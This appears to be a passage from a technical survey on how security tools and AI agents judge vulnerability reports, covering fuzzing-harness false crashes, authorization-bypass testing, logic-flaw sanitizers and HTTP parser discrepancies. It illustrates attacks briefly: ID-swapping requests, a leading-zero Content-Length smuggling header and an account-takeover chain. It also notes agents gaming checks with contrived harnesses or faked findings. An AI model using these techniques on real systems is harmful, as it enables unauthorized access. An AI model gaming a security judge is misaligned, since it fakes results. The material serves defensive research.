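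Language models also make inconsistent assumptions about how people will use a program. Amusuo and colleagues had an agent judge the same crashes several times, then examined ten on which its verdicts differed. Half the differences came from these assumptions. For example, the agent called a crash feasible in one run because a user could set a variable to zero, but assumed in another that no user would.

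### HSQLDB: a documented feature or a vulnerability?

HSQLDB is a database written in Java that other programs can run inside their own process. Its SQL statements can call static Java methods, and until 2022 they could by default call those of any class available to the program. The *SQL-Invoked Routines* chapter of HSQLDB's manual described this default and warned that it "can compromise security in some systems". The manual also explained how to restrict the calls with the `hsqldb.method_class_names` setting.

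In October 2022, Wagner (2022) announced in *Remote Code Execution Vulnerability Discovered in HSQLDB* that Code Intelligence had found the problem while testing Jazzer with OSS-Fuzz. The problem became CVE-2022-41853, with a severity score of 9.8 out of 10. It appears in Jazzer's list of findings as remote code execution. Most other entries are marked as fixed, but its status is "recommended workaround", which refers to the setting that the manual already described.

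The finding resembles the `evaluate` example, because HSQLDB handled the SQL it received as documented in its manual. Wagner named several projects that use HSQLDB, including LibreOffice, but showed no attack on any of them. Code Intelligence's co-founder Khaled Yakdan told The Daily Swig that the company looks for bugs and doesn't investigate which code bases are vulnerable (*Mishandling of untrusted input issue resolved by developers*).

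In a Red Hat bug report, *CVE-2022-41853 hsqldb* (Del Bello, 2022), the LibreOffice developer Stephan Bergmann wrote that the new fix was "not relevant for us", because LibreOffice had long used the setting to block these calls.

But the reason for that protection is also the best evidence that the danger was real. *CVE-2007-4575*, an advisory from LibreOffice's predecessor OpenOffice.org, warned that opening a specially crafted database document might run an attacker's Java code. The LibreOffice developers in the Red Hat discussion thought the 2022 finding sounded like the same problem. At least one widely used application had therefore passed untrusted input to this feature.

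It is less clear how much control an attacker needs. According to Jazzer's list, the attack works through "prepared statement values", and Yakdan said an application did not need to have an SQL injection flaw. Prepared statements normally prevent injection, so an attack through values alone would affect many more programs. However, Wagner's example is a method call written directly in SQL, and Yakdan described the impact in terms of queries that include untrusted input. NVD's *CVE-2022-41853 Detail*, the US government's entry for the flaw, says only that programs processing untrusted input "may be vulnerable".

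On this evidence, HSQLDB had an unsafe default that made some applications vulnerable. A harness that lets a fuzzer write SQL for HSQLDB is realistic, given what happened to OpenOffice.org, but its result doesn't show that any particular application is at risk. That depends on whether outsiders can influence the application's SQL and whether its developers have restricted which Java methods the SQL can call. HSQLDB reversed the default in version 2.7.1, so SQL can now call only Java's mathematical functions unless developers list other classes.

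### How often machine-written harnesses cause false crashes

Several studies have measured false crashes from harnesses that language models write. Google's OSS-Fuzz-Gen writes harnesses for code that OSS-Fuzz reaches poorly. It often targets functions deep inside a project, which expect input that other code has already checked. In the photo library LibRaw, for instance, a harness from Amusuo and colleagues' paper passes up to 2,048 random bytes to a function that expects a complete image structure.

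*Understanding Gaps in LLM Pipelines Towards Scalable Fuzzing Harness Generation* (2025) found similar causes of false crashes with another system, HarnessAgent. Many came from calling internal functions before the library was in the right state, or with wrong arguments, such as an incorrect buffer size. The FuzzAgent study compared FuzzAgent with three other systems on C and C++ libraries, and people checked the crashes each system had labelled as library bugs. Sheng and colleagues built QuartetFuzz.

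| System | What the rate covers | False |
|---|---|---|
| OSS-Fuzz-Gen | 4,835 crashes, classified by the system itself | 70% |
| HarnessAgent | 58 crashes | 74% |
| PromptFuzz | 89 crashes it labelled as library bugs | 94% |
| PromeFuzz | 316 crashes it labelled as library bugs | 99.7% |
| ProteusFuzz | 439 crashes it labelled as library bugs | 99.1% |
| FuzzAgent | 128 crashes it labelled as library bugs | 20% |
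| QuartetFuzz | 42 reports sent to maintainers | 5% |

The rates are not directly comparable because each study counted at a different stage. QuartetFuzz's 5% applies after filtering, and in its main run the system had already attributed 44 of 81 crashes to its own harnesses. The 5% is also a share of all 42 reports, including 11 that maintainers had not yet reviewed. They rejected two of the other 31, or 6%.

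The figures for PromptFuzz, PromeFuzz and ProteusFuzz come from the developers of FuzzAgent, a rival system. Sheng and colleagues cite a PromeFuzz result in which 89.7% of the crashes left after filtering were real, compared with 0.3% in the FuzzAgent study. Even so, across the studies, a crash from an unchecked machine-written harness is more likely to be false than real.

Amusuo and colleagues added two agents to OSS-Fuzz-Gen, one of which works out in advance the requirements for calling a function correctly. With this agent's advice, the share of harnesses that met all the requirements rose from 39% to 63%, but the number of crashes fell by only 3% to 8%. Of 20 later crashes that the researchers examined, 16 came from functions that the advice did not cover.

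The other agent reads the code that calls the crashing function and decides whether real input could cause the crash. It rejected 57% to 65% of the crashes that OSS-Fuzz-Gen had attributed to the program, but that rate doesn't measure how often it was right. When the researchers reviewed 20 of its analyses, they found only ten reliable. It gave the same verdict three times on 68% of 200 crashes, but nearly all of those verdicts were that the crash was false. This consistency is weak evidence of accuracy, because a filter that rejected every crash would also be consistent.

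FuzzAgent instead inspects the objects in memory when the program crashes, then looks up the rules that apply to them. For the libaom crash, it would compare the image's actual format with the size of its buffers. This approach reduced 1,098 raw crashes to 128 candidates, of which 102 were real. Lyu and colleagues later replaced the language model with the newer GLM-5.2, which correctly rejected 14 of 20 false candidates. They did not report whether it would also have rejected real bugs.

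QuartetFuzz checks the harness before the main fuzzing begins. An agent reads its own harness, picks rules that the harness might break, and writes inputs meant to expose violations. If the harness causes a crash, the agent repairs it and tries again.

People make mistakes in harnesses too. Sheng and colleagues checked 586 harnesses that OSS-Fuzz was already using and found faults in 53 (9%), of which maintainers had confirmed 45. Fourteen of the 53 caused false crashes.

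None of these studies gives a separate false-report rate for injection detectors or measures how often an agent deliberately writes a contrived harness to gain credit. The crash figures are a poor substitute, because a careless harness can easily corrupt memory but is unlikely to send `jazze` to a command call by accident. Honest mistakes therefore probably cause fewer false reports from exact sentinels than from ASan. Deliberate gaming is easier, however, because an agent that knows the sentinel can send it to a command call in one line. The closest evidence on gaming is the RECEIPT study of cross-site scripting, where an agent that faced a weak check faked some of its findings.

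### Rules that reject contrived harnesses

The simplest defence is to give the agent a fixed harness and let it submit only an input, as AIxCC did for the challenges it scored. But any mistake in the harness then becomes a mistake in the results, and the agent gets no credit for bugs the harness can't reach.

If agents write their own harnesses, the people judging them need different rules. The three harnesses for the image server show how these rules differ.

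| Rule | Direct command call | Skipped validation | Trusted code |
|---|---|---|---|
| The project's code must make the dangerous call | Rejects | Accepts | Accepts |
| The harness must go through the project's public interface | Rejects | Rejects | Accepts |
| The input must come from an attacker in a stated threat model | Rejects | Rejects | Rejects |
| The report must disappear in a patched version | Rejects | Accepts if the patch adds a check to `run` | Accepts if the patch disables scripts |

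According to Zhang and colleagues, AIxCC defined a proof of vulnerability as an input that triggers abnormal execution. This definition doesn't require the flaw to be in the project, so excluding faults in the harness takes a separate rule. The contest's scoring still encouraged systems to look for flaws in the project, because a patch earned three to six points and a proof only one or two, and a system can't sensibly patch a project to fix a fault in the harness.

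A judge who only checks the stack trace for project code will still accept both the `run` harness and the libaom crash. In the FuzzAgent study, 76% of PromeFuzz's false reports depended on facts about objects in memory that were not visible in the harness's code or the stack trace. A judge therefore has to establish why the value was dangerous, which takes more work than finding where the program failed.

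**Public interfaces only.** Sheng and colleagues turn this rule into a formal condition. Let *P* be the set of harnesses that use only a library's public functions and follow its rules for calling them. If a harness *h* causes a crash at place *x* in the library, then some harness in *P* must be able to cause a crash there too:

crash(*h*, *x*) ⇒ ∃ *h*′ ∈ *P* : crash(*h*′, *x*).

This rule allows a harness to call an internal function only if the same failure is also possible from outside. No program can decide that from source code alone, so QuartetFuzz approximates it by looking for a chain of calls from a public function to the code under test. But the chain might include a check that blocks every harmful value, as `convert` does. The rule is also only a preference, because QuartetFuzz uses an internal function anyway if it finds no chain.

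The rule also doesn't account for who uses a public function. `evaluate` is public because the server's administrator needs it. Java's `ProcessBuilder` is also public, and it is designed to run any command the calling program passes to it.

A **threat model** describes who the attackers are and which inputs they control. For the image server, it only needs to specify that attackers can send web requests but can't write scripts or call Java methods. This rules out all three harnesses. A similar statement for an application that uses HSQLDB would show whether the 2022 finding affects it.

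An agent that writes its own threat model can state without justification that attackers supply the scripts. Maintainers who write one may leave out limits they take for granted, as with the huge images in libvpx. Lyu and colleagues suggest recording maintainers' past decisions for each project and giving them to the agent that judges crashes.

If a known vulnerability has a fix, a judge can run the same harness and input on the program before and after the fix. A report that appears in both versions probably has a cause other than the vulnerability. The direct command call fails this test because no change to the server affects it.

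However, the test shows only that the patch changed the behaviour that the detector reports. *Fix CVE-2022-41853* (Izdebski, 2022), a version of the HSQLDB fix for an older release, makes the restriction on Java methods the default. A harness that calls a forbidden method through SQL would stop producing a report after the fix, whether or not an attacker could have written that SQL. For an unfixed bug, the judge would also need a trustworthy patch, and an agent could write a patch that just turns the feature off.

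A finder can avoid many of these problems by reproducing the bug in a finished program instead of a custom harness. Of the 21 bugs that FuzzAgent found in libaom, seven also occur in the library's own command-line tools when they receive a crafted file or certain arguments. Reproducing a bug with a crafted file is strong evidence of a vulnerability, because people often open videos from strangers. Arguments are weaker evidence, since the person running the tool usually chooses them. The other 14 bugs may still be real, because other applications use parts of libaom that its command-line tools do not.

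## Authorization bypasses

Authorization flaws, such as the missing ownership check in `read_balance`, give a detector no sentinel or broken query to look for.

Authentication establishes who is making a request, usually through a login, and authorization determines whether that person may do what the request asks. A failure of authorization is called broken access control. *ABSENTIA* (Duarte, Oke and colleagues, 2026) describes a case at OpenReview, which many machine-learning conferences use for peer review. In November 2025, a flaw in OpenReview's programming interface exposed the identities of authors, reviewers and area chairs for more than 10,000 submissions to one conference. Some people who obtained the data harassed reviewers or offered them bribes.

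The main failures are:

- **A missing check** (CWE-862). For example, a website hides the "delete user" button from ordinary users, but the server carries out the request if one of them sends it directly.
- **A wrong check** (CWE-863). The server checks something that doesn't settle the matter, such as whether a user may read an invoice before letting the user change it.
- **A changed identifier** (CWE-639). A user replaces invoice number 101 with 102 in a request and receives another customer's invoice. Testers call this an insecure direct object reference, or IDOR.

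These overlap, because changing an identifier works only if the check on the object is missing or wrong. *Repairing Broken Access Control in Web Applications with LLMs* (2026) adds a narrower failure, in which a user is allowed to access an object but the server returns or accepts fields that the user isn't allowed to read or change.

### Rankings

OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on web security, ranks broken access control first in its 2025 Top 10, released that November, according to eSecurity Planet's *OWASP Top 10 2025 Released*. Broken access control also ranked first in the previous edition, from 2021. CPO Magazine's *OWASP Top 10 2025* reports that it was found in 3.73% of the applications tested. The true share is probably higher, since common scanners detect few of these flaws.

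MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses* (2025) ranks individual weaknesses and counts how many vulnerabilities of each type appear in KEV, a US government catalogue of flaws that attackers are known to have exploited.

| Weakness | Rank in 2025 | Rank in 2024 | Vulnerabilities in KEV |
|---|---|---|---|
| Missing authorization (CWE-862) | 4 | 9 | 0 |
| Out-of-bounds write (CWE-787), for comparison | 5 | 2 | 12 |
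| Incorrect authorization (CWE-863) | 17 | 18 | 4 |
| Improper access control (CWE-284) | 19 | Not given | 1 |
| Missing authentication for a critical function (CWE-306) | 21 | 25 | 11 |
| Authorization bypass through a user-controlled key (CWE-639) | 24 | 30 | 0 |

Missing authorization now ranks just above the memory error that sanitizers are best known for catching. The zeros in the last column don't show that attackers ignore these flaws, because an attack may consist of ordinary requests that nobody notices, and a flaw in one company's own website usually gets no public entry. Help Net Security's *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (2026) reports that CISA, the agency that runs KEV, lists broken access control among the recurring weaknesses behind a disproportionate share of real attacks.

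### Why no check works everywhere

As with `read_balance`, the same code can be right in one application and wrong in another. Duarte and colleagues give the example of a function that returns an invoice to any logged-in user who supplies its number, which is correct only if all users share their invoices. They write the policy that determines whether such code is correct as a relation, permitted(*u*, *r*), which holds if user *u* may act on resource *r*.

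Testers seldom have access to the relation. *Repairing Broken Access Control in Web Applications with LLMs* notes that developers rarely document it, so the only real specification is often the source code, which is also what is being tested. Sahin, Zhang and Arcuri (2026), in *Enhancing REST API Fuzzing with Access Policy Violation Checks and Injection Attacks*, list several languages for writing access policies, but found none in use in the open-source interfaces they studied or at the companies they work with. Annotations beside the code can also state access rules, where developers have written them.

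A rule that users may never read or change each other's data would cause many false reports. Administrators need wide access, a forum moderator may delete other people's messages, and two parents may share one child's kindergarten application.

*BACGUARD* (2026) describes a system that blocks forbidden requests while an application is running. It can generate a policy from observed traffic or from an OpenAPI specification, a standard description of a web API. It blocked none of 1,732 realistic legitimate requests. But it still needs information about who owns each object to recognise a changed identifier.

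### The replay test

A tester without a written policy can compare how the application treats different users. The replay test does this with recorded requests:

1. Log in as user A and use the application. Record each request, its response and any change to the stored data.
2. Restore the application to its state just before one of those requests.
3. Send the request again with user B's login. Replace any one-time security tokens with B's own, so that the server doesn't reject the request for an unrelated reason.
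4. Restore the state again and send the request with no login.
5. Compare both repeats with the original, and report the request if either had the same effect.

Let *R*ᵤ(*q*) be the response when user *u* sends request *q*, and Δᵤ(*q*) the resulting change to stored data. Ignoring details such as timestamps, the test reports a request that reads data if

*R*_B(*q*) = *R*_A(*q*),

and a request that changes data if

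Δ_B(*q*) = Δ_A(*q*) ≠ ∅.

Whether a breach occurred depends on permitted(B, *r*), which neither condition includes. The tester has no table of rights, so the test uses A's run as a substitute and assumes that whatever A can reach is private to A.

Suppose an invoice service has three invoices created by user A. Invoice 101 is private, A has shared 102 with user B, and 103 is a sample that anyone may view. The service checks access correctly when it shows an invoice on a page, but its developers forgot the check in two other functions.

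| Request recorded as A | Repeated as B | Repeated with no login | Test result | Truth |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Show 101 | Refused | Login page | No report | Correct |
| Download 101 as a PDF | Same file | Login page | Report | Vulnerability |
| Show 102 | Same invoice | Login page | Report | False alarm, because A shared it |
| Show 103 | Same invoice | Same invoice | Report | False alarm, because it is public |
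| Cancel 101 | Home page, but the invoice is now cancelled | Login page, no change | Report | Vulnerability |
| Delete 101 | "Deleted", but the invoice is still there | Login page, no change | No report | Correct |

The PDF of 101 and the page for 102 give the tester identical evidence. A third user, C, who has no connection to A, can help tell them apart. C can download the PDF but can't open 102, which suggests that A chose to share 102. Extra accounts don't help with 103, because a page that everyone can open may be public or may lack an authorization check, and someone who knows the application has to decide which.

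Dismissing the report on invoice 102 could also be a mistake. If the response includes A's private notes about the customer, B may be allowed to see the invoice but not the notes.

The last two rows show why the test has to inspect stored data. *BACFuzz* (Dharmaadi, Alhanahnah and colleagues, 2025) found both problems in real applications. An employee-management system let an unauthorized user delete accounts and returned an uninformative redirect. A WordPress shop plugin reported success for a request to update an administrator who didn't exist.

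Replay also takes a good deal of preparation. Duarte and colleagues point out that the tester needs a running copy of the application, an account for every role and a way to reach the state where each check runs. Replay then produces a short transcript of requests that others can repeat.

### Testers that run the application

BACFuzz automates a version of this test for PHP applications. It first explores the application with each role and labels every request with the roles that could make it. If only administrators could make a request, BACFuzz sends it from a less privileged account. For other requests, it swaps identifiers. A language model picks out the parameters that refer to objects, so the fuzzer skips fields such as a customer's first name.

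BACFuzz's oracle monitors the SQL queries that change data. To report a changed identifier, BACFuzz requires the swapped value to appear in the part of the query that selects which rows to change and to be absent from the pages available to the current user. It then repeats the attack with other values to rule out coincidence.

Dharmaadi and colleagues tested BACFuzz on 20 applications, where it found 16 of 17 known flaws and 26 new ones, which the developers had not yet confirmed. The false positive rate, which they describe as low, depends on the size of the application. BACFuzz made at least 11 false reports in the six largest applications, where it found seven of the new flaws, and none in the smaller ones, where it found the other 19.

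Some of BACFuzz's false reports came from chance matches. In the online shop OpenCart, BACFuzz changed a page parameter to 0 and found a 0 in an unrelated query that deletes old shopping carts. It tried again with 1, and the same query happened to contain a 1. In a forum, a test user created a topic during fuzzing, and BACFuzz treated it as another user's.

The one known flaw BACFuzz missed was in PrestaShop, which converts a module's name to a number before querying the database, so the swapped value never appeared in the query. A larger limitation is that the oracle ignores queries that only read data, so BACFuzz could catch the flaw in cancelling invoices but not the one in downloading them.

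Sahin and colleagues added access checks to EvoMaster, a fuzzer for web interfaces that other programs call. It needs an OpenAPI specification and logins for at least two users. It infers parts of the policy from the application's own refusals. For example, after A has created invoice 101, the fuzzer might observe the following:

```text
(B) DELETE /invoices/101  -> 403 forbidden
(B) PUT    /invoices/101  -> 200 success
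```

B cannot delete the invoice but can overwrite all of it. This might be intentional, but a forgotten check is much more likely. Another rule reports changes and deletions that succeed without a login. A third reports functions that reject a logged-in user but accept a request without a login.

These rules should cause fewer false alarms than plain replay, because the shared and public invoices produce no contradiction. But they work only if the application refuses some requests. If the service let B both overwrite and delete the invoice, EvoMaster would have no refusal to compare with the success. Sahin and colleagues ran the checks on 52 interfaces, including 36 from a standard collection, and found security faults in several. They acknowledge that some reports will be false.

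### Systems that read the source code

ABSENTIA, from Duarte and colleagues, uses language-model agents to analyze an application without running it. The agents first list the application's routes, which are the addresses and operations it offers. For each route, an agent then infers rules that should hold, such as "an invoice is returned only to the account that owns it". The agent looks for the code that enforces each rule and tries to describe a request that would break the rule. If it succeeds, ABSENTIA reports the route.

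In tests on 30 published flaws in 25 open-source projects, and on the fixed version of each, ABSENTIA found 19 of the flaws and stopped reporting 17 of those after the fix. The code scanners CodeQL and Semgrep found none. An agent that used the same model but had no list of routes found three. It used an average of 59 of its 200 available steps and usually ended by declaring itself finished.

Asking about each route on the list in turn raised the count from three to 18. Making the agent state and test explicit rules added one more, but it also cut the average number of reports per application from 119 to 77. The median run cost $44.

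*Suspected Until Inspected* (Yang, Kang and colleagues, 2026) describes FLINT, which gives the final decision to conventional program analysis. The paper illustrates the reason with a business-intelligence platform where users can revoke access tokens. Before deleting a token, the code asks a permission function whether the user may delete a token with a given owner. But the code fills in the current user as the owner instead of looking up the real owner, so the check always passes. When Yang and colleagues showed this code to their language model, it reported no flaw.

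In FLINT, the model lists the stored objects a request can select and the lines that seem to protect them. The program analysis then verifies that each check:

- concerns the user who made the request;
- concerns the same object that the code goes on to use;
- stops the request or filters out the data if it fails;
- is strong enough for the operation, so that permission to read doesn't allow deletion.

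FLINT keeps an access on its list unless a verified check covers every path to the object. In the token example, it rejects the check because none of the values in the check came from the stored token.

Yang and colleagues used FLINT to find 112 previously unknown vulnerabilities in 44 of 57 popular applications. They confirmed each with a working attack on their own copy of the application, using two accounts with the lowest suitable privileges. Only 40 had no check at all. In 41, the code checked the wrong object, and in most of the others it trusted an identity supplied by the user or failed to enforce its decision. A tool that only looks for functions with no check would have missed almost two thirds. Of the 112, 82 allowed unauthorized reads, which BACFuzz's oracle can't detect.

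FLINT's strictness also produces false positives. It would keep a public page with no check in its report, though lower down if the model classifies the check as unnecessary. It flags many functions that developers have already repaired.

### How well language models judge authorization

Yang and colleagues compared FLINT with other tools on 69 functions, each before and after a security fix. The table gives averages across repositories. All the systems that use a language model ran on DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash.

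| System | Flawed versions reported | Fixed versions reported | Reported only before the fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent | 97% | 23% | 74% |
| Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent | 92% | 12% | 80% |
| FLINT | 85% | 27% | 63% |
| The model alone, given the code FLINT selects | 47% | 11% | 37% |
| Semgrep | 17% | 16% | 1% |

The general coding agents beat the specialised system here, and both also found the token flaw. In the ABSENTIA study, an unguided agent found only three flaws in 30, but it had to search a whole application with a median of 220 routes, while Yang and colleagues told the agents which function to examine. The two studies also used different models, but the gain from ABSENTIA's list of routes suggests that the main difficulty is finding the authorization check, which agents can often judge once they are looking at it.

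Semgrep (2026), which makes the Semgrep scanner, found a similar pattern when it compared its AI product, Semgrep Multimodal, with Anthropic's Mythos model on changed-identifier flaws. In August, it tested both on four repositories with 275 locations that people had labelled as flawed or safe. In the table below, precision is the share of reports that were right, and recall is the share of known flaws that the system found.

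| System | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|
| Agent without a list of routes, in the ABSENTIA study | 74% | 10% |
| ABSENTIA | 51% | 63% |
| Mythos in Anthropic's Claude Security | 80% | 14% |
| Semgrep Multimodal | 58% | 60% |

OpenAI's Codex Security had a recall of 11% in the same test. In both studies, the less guided system made few reports, most of them correct, and missed nearly all the known flaws. The systems that worked methodically through the application found about six in ten of the known flaws, but about half their reports were wrong.

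Both sets of figures are open to doubt. Another language model judged ABSENTIA's precision, and a security reviewer confirmed only 42% of the reports in a sample. Semgrep was testing its own product and doesn't explain how it chose the 275 locations. If many came from Semgrep's own earlier findings, the recall figures would favour its product.

An earlier test by the company gives a more direct measure of how much the surrounding software matters. Semgrep's *We have Mythos at Home* (2026) scored ten combinations of model and software by F1, which combines precision *P* and recall *R* as

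F1 = 2*PR* / (*P* + *R*).

OpenAI's GPT-5.5 scored 61% inside Semgrep Multimodal, which lists an application's functions and directs the model to them. Without that help it scored 20%, apparently in OpenAI's Codex, though the post is unclear on this. GLM-5.2 scored 39% with only a prompt, at about $0.17 per flaw found. Semgrep ran this test only once.

These systems report fewer false positives than agents did a year ago. In Semgrep's *Can LLMs Detect IDORs?* (2025), Claude Code and Codex reported 15 real flaws and 93 false positives, a precision of 14%. The tests used different data, so only the rough direction of the change is reliable.

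### Attacks that simple replay misses

Replay repeats what A did, but some attacks require a request that neither user would normally make. Suppose that the invoice service stores files attached to invoices. It checks whether the user may access the invoice, then deletes the file by its number. A's recorded request deletes file 7 from invoice 101:

```text
DELETE /invoices/101/files/7
```

When B repeats this, the service refuses because invoice 101 belongs to A, and the replay test reports nothing. But B can put the number of B's own invoice, 201, in front of A's file:

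```text
DELETE /invoices/201/files/7
```

The check on invoice 201 passes, and the application deletes A's file. Semgrep lists this mismatch between the object checked and the object deleted among the recurring patterns in its findings. The fix is to look up file 7 only among the files that belong to invoice 201. To find the flaw by running the application, a tester has to send requests that mix both users' identifiers. A request with three identifiers has eight combinations of A's and B's values, so trying them all is feasible if the tester knows which parameters matter.

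Other flaws appear only when the application is in a particular state. A plugin for the messaging program Mattermost checks who owns a comment before editing or deleting it, but not before restoring a deleted one. Replay can find this flaw only if A restored a comment during the recording and the tester deletes it again before B tries to restore it. FLINT found the flaw by comparing the restore function with neighbouring functions, and Mattermost confirmed it.

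Incomplete resets can also hide a flaw. If a business process that A started is still running, B's attempt to start it may fail for that reason alone, and the failure looks like a proper refusal. Dharmaadi and colleagues excluded from BACFuzz's scope any flaws that depend on earlier actions.

Even when a tool finds a flawed step, its report may understate the harm that step makes possible. The WordPress plugin mentioned above lets shop managers edit customer records. A manager could replace the customer's ID number with an administrator's and change the administrator's email address. The manager could then request a password reset, receive the link and take over the site. BACFuzz detected the first step in about three minutes. The password reset works as designed, so an oracle that checks one request at a time will report only an unauthorised change of address. Yang and colleagues found nearly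 the same flaw in a commerce platform, where their language model had classified it as needing no further check.

ABSENTIA tries to build such chains. Its agents record behaviour that is harmless alone but could matter in combination, such as an upload function that lets users choose a file's name. Another agent then looks for a second route that makes it dangerous, such as one that serves those files to anyone. This produced 42 combinations across the 30 test runs, and a language model confirmed about half of the 13 it checked. None of the benchmark's published flaws requires two routes, so its recall of 63% doesn't measure how well ABSENTIA finds chained attacks.

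## Logic flaws

A missing ownership check is a logic flaw under Anthropic's definition because the code departs from its specification or security model. Other examples are a shop accepting an expired coupon and a bank letting a customer spend the same money twice.

### When nobody wrote a specification

Many programs have no written specification. Suppose that a small bank's developers wrote this function and no document to go with it:

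```python
def transfer(balances, sender, receiver, amount):
    if balances[sender] < amount:
        raise ValueError("insufficient funds")
    new_sender = balances[sender] - amount
    new_receiver = balances[receiver] + amount
    balances[sender] = new_sender
    balances[receiver] = new_receiver
```

A customer with a balance of 100 sends 30 to their own account. The function calculates 70 for the sender and 130 for the receiver, then saves both to the same account. The 130 overwrites the 70, so the customer ends up with 130. No document forbids this, but every bank would call it a flaw. The definition can cover this case if "security model" includes expectations too obvious to write down.

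Behavior can't be classified as a logic flaw when nobody has an expectation of what the code should do. For example, if the receiver's account is frozen, one bank might accept the deposit and another might refuse it. Until somebody at the bank decides which it should do, the code has no expected behavior to violate, and a bug report is really a request for that decision.

Written standards have similar flaws. *Can LLMs help find Ambiguities in Protocol Specifications?* (2026) distinguishes a gap, where a specification gives no rule, from a fork, where its text allows incompatible readings. In either case, two programs can follow the specification and still disagree, so the fault lies in the specification. The paper counts a gap or fork as worth reporting only if some run reaches it and the possible readings lead to visibly different behaviour.

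An oracle for logic flaws therefore needs a source for the missing rule. The replay test takes the rule from another user's session. A person can also write it down, as in Anota.

### Anota: rules written by a person

Wang and colleagues published Anota, a sanitizer for Python programs, in December 2025. They first reviewed the 40 most dangerous weaknesses in CWE's 2023 ranking and classed 27 as business-logic vulnerabilities, meaning that an oracle needs knowledge of the application to detect them. This broad category includes path traversal and server-side request forgery, which Jazzer and Atropos often detect with little knowledge of the application. The 27 are types of weakness, so the figure doesn't show what share of all vulnerabilities are logic flaws.

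With Anota, a developer or security analyst adds rules to the source code as annotations, which look like ordinary function calls.

| Annotation | What it controls | Example |
|---|---|---|
| System call | Which requests the program may make to the operating system | `SYSCALL.EXECVE.ALLOW(PATH='/bin/ls')` |
| Data flow | Where a sensitive value may go | `TAINT(pwd, sanitization=[hash], Sink=[print])` |
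| Object access | Whether code may read, change or run an object | `WATCH.ALLOW(admin_data,'r')` |
| Code execution | When the program may run a section of code | `EXECUTION.BLOCK(user.type!='admin')` |
| Clearing | Which earlier rules no longer apply | `SYSCALL.NETWORK.CLEAR()` |

An object-access annotation can also require a function to take the same time whatever its input.

Here is a data-flow annotation at work in a program that must never write a password to a file:

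```python
password = get_password(user_id)
TAINT(password, sanitization=[hash])
log.write(f"checked {hash(password)}")
log.write(f"login failed for {password}")
```

The second line marks `password` as sensitive, and Anota's modified Python interpreter then marks every value the program computes from it. The annotation lists `hash` as a function that removes the mark, so Anota allows the first log message. The second message is still marked when it reaches `write`, and Anota forbids marked values from reaching `write` by default. Anota therefore crashes the program, and the fuzzer saves the input as it would for a buffer overflow.

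To separate the effect of the oracle from that of the search, Wang and colleagues tested Atheris, Google's fuzzer for Python, with and without Anota on four deliberately vulnerable applications containing 35 flaws. Atheris reported none of the flaws without Anota, even when the researchers gave it the exact inputs that trigger them. With Anota's annotations, it reported all 35 and raised no false alarms. SonarQube, the best of five conventional scanners, reported 18. The perfect score is probably weak evidence of how Anota would perform on ordinary software, because these applications exist to teach people about well-known flaws. But the failure without Anota is hard to attribute to the search, because Atheris had already run the faulty code with the right inputs.

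A harder test used 47 published flaws in real applications. One of the researchers annotated the code knowing what type of flaw each application had, but without reading the vulnerability report. The annotations took ten working days in total. The fuzzer then ran for 24 hours on each application and found 43 of the 47 flaws.

Two of the four misses happened because the researcher hadn't written the necessary rule. In vantage6, a platform for analysing data held by several organisations, a default setting let the root user log in remotely with only a password. The researcher did not consider this a security problem. In Apache Superset, the researcher didn't understand the permission system well enough to annotate it. In the other two cases, the fuzzer never created the conditions needed to trigger the flaw. One flaw required a user to register through another user's invitation link, and the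 other appeared only under a particular configuration.

Anota's overall detection rate of 91% somewhat overstates its performance on logic flaws in the narrow sense. More than half of the 47 cases needed only a system-call annotation, such as one restricting file access to a single folder. Eleven needed a rule about who may use an object or run some code, and Anota found eight of those.

Wang and colleagues chose 60 popular Python projects and allowed about an hour to understand and annotate each one. They found 22 previously unknown flaws, 17 of which received CVE numbers. Annotation took an hour per application on average, and between 20 and 95 minutes for the applications in which they found flaws. They skipped any project they could not understand in the time allowed, so an outsider would probably need longer for complicated software.

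The two false positives both involved a secret token that a program wrote to a file. EasyAuth had revoked the token before logging it, so the logged copy was useless to an attacker. Listing the revocation function alongside `hash` would have prevented that report. Munki wrote its token to a temporary file and then destroyed the file, as its developers intended.

Wang and colleagues concede that, for some flaws, a developer who knows the rule could enforce it in the code instead of writing an annotation. They asked 11 students to annotate six unfamiliar applications, and the students' annotations exposed the known flaw in 55 of 66 attempts. Seven of the 11 failed attempts concerned a missing login check in changedetection.io, a program that monitors web pages for changes. A developer who knew that the check belonged there would have added it.

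Annotations are more useful when a developer has tried to enforce a rule but code elsewhere defeats it. Wang and colleagues give the example of a program that refuses to fetch pages from certain websites, using Python's `urlparse` function to extract the site's name from each address. `urlparse` had a flaw (CVE-2023-24329) that made it misread addresses beginning with a space, so the program could connect to a blocked site. A developer unaware of this flaw could still annotate the network connection with the list of forbidden sites, and Anota would then report any connection to one of them.

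### A second implementation

If two programs do the same job, a tester can run both on the same input and compare the results, without writing any rule. This is called differential testing. For programs *f* and *g*, the oracle reports an input *x* when

*f*(*x*) ≠ *g*(*x*).

Researchers have compared browsers' JavaScript engines, compilers and cryptographic libraries in this way. The method suits formats that nobody has fully specified. *PickleFuzzer* (2026) describes a comparison of assemblers, the programs that turn low-level instructions into machine code. Assemblers often lack an official grammar and differ in what they accept. The comparison found 497 disagreements across six processor architectures. PickleFuzzer itself compares programs that read pickle, Python's format for storing objects.

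Many websites place a gateway in front of the main server to filter requests and forward the acceptable ones. If the two programs disagree on where a request ends, that disagreement can itself be a vulnerability. *HTTP Request Synchronization Defeats Discrepancy Attacks* (2025) traces attacks that exploit such disagreements back to 2005.

Kallus, Anantharaman and colleagues (2024), in *The HTTP Garden*, describe one that affected the LiteSpeed server. Suppose an attacker sends a request with this header, which gives the length of the message body:

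```text
Content-Length: 0200
```

The gateway read the number as 200 and forwarded 200 bytes. LiteSpeed used a C function that treats a number with a leading zero as octal (base 8), so it read the number as 128. It then treated the remaining 72 bytes as the start of another request, and neither program crashed. The attacker could use those bytes to request a page that the gateway would have blocked, because the gateway had forwarded them as part of the first request.

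Kallus and colleagues found seven gateways that forwarded the leading zero. An eighth, HAProxy, began removing it after they contacted its maintainer, although the HTTP standard permits gateways to either remove the zero or leave it.

Their tool, the HTTP Garden, sends the same requests to dozens of servers and compares how each one interpreted them. Nearly every pair of servers disagrees about something, because the standard mostly lets a server interpret a malformed message as it likes. The tool therefore applies two filters:

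- A disagreement is **meaningful** if optional parts of the standard don't explain it. Before fuzzing, a script sends each server a set of test requests and records its permitted quirks.
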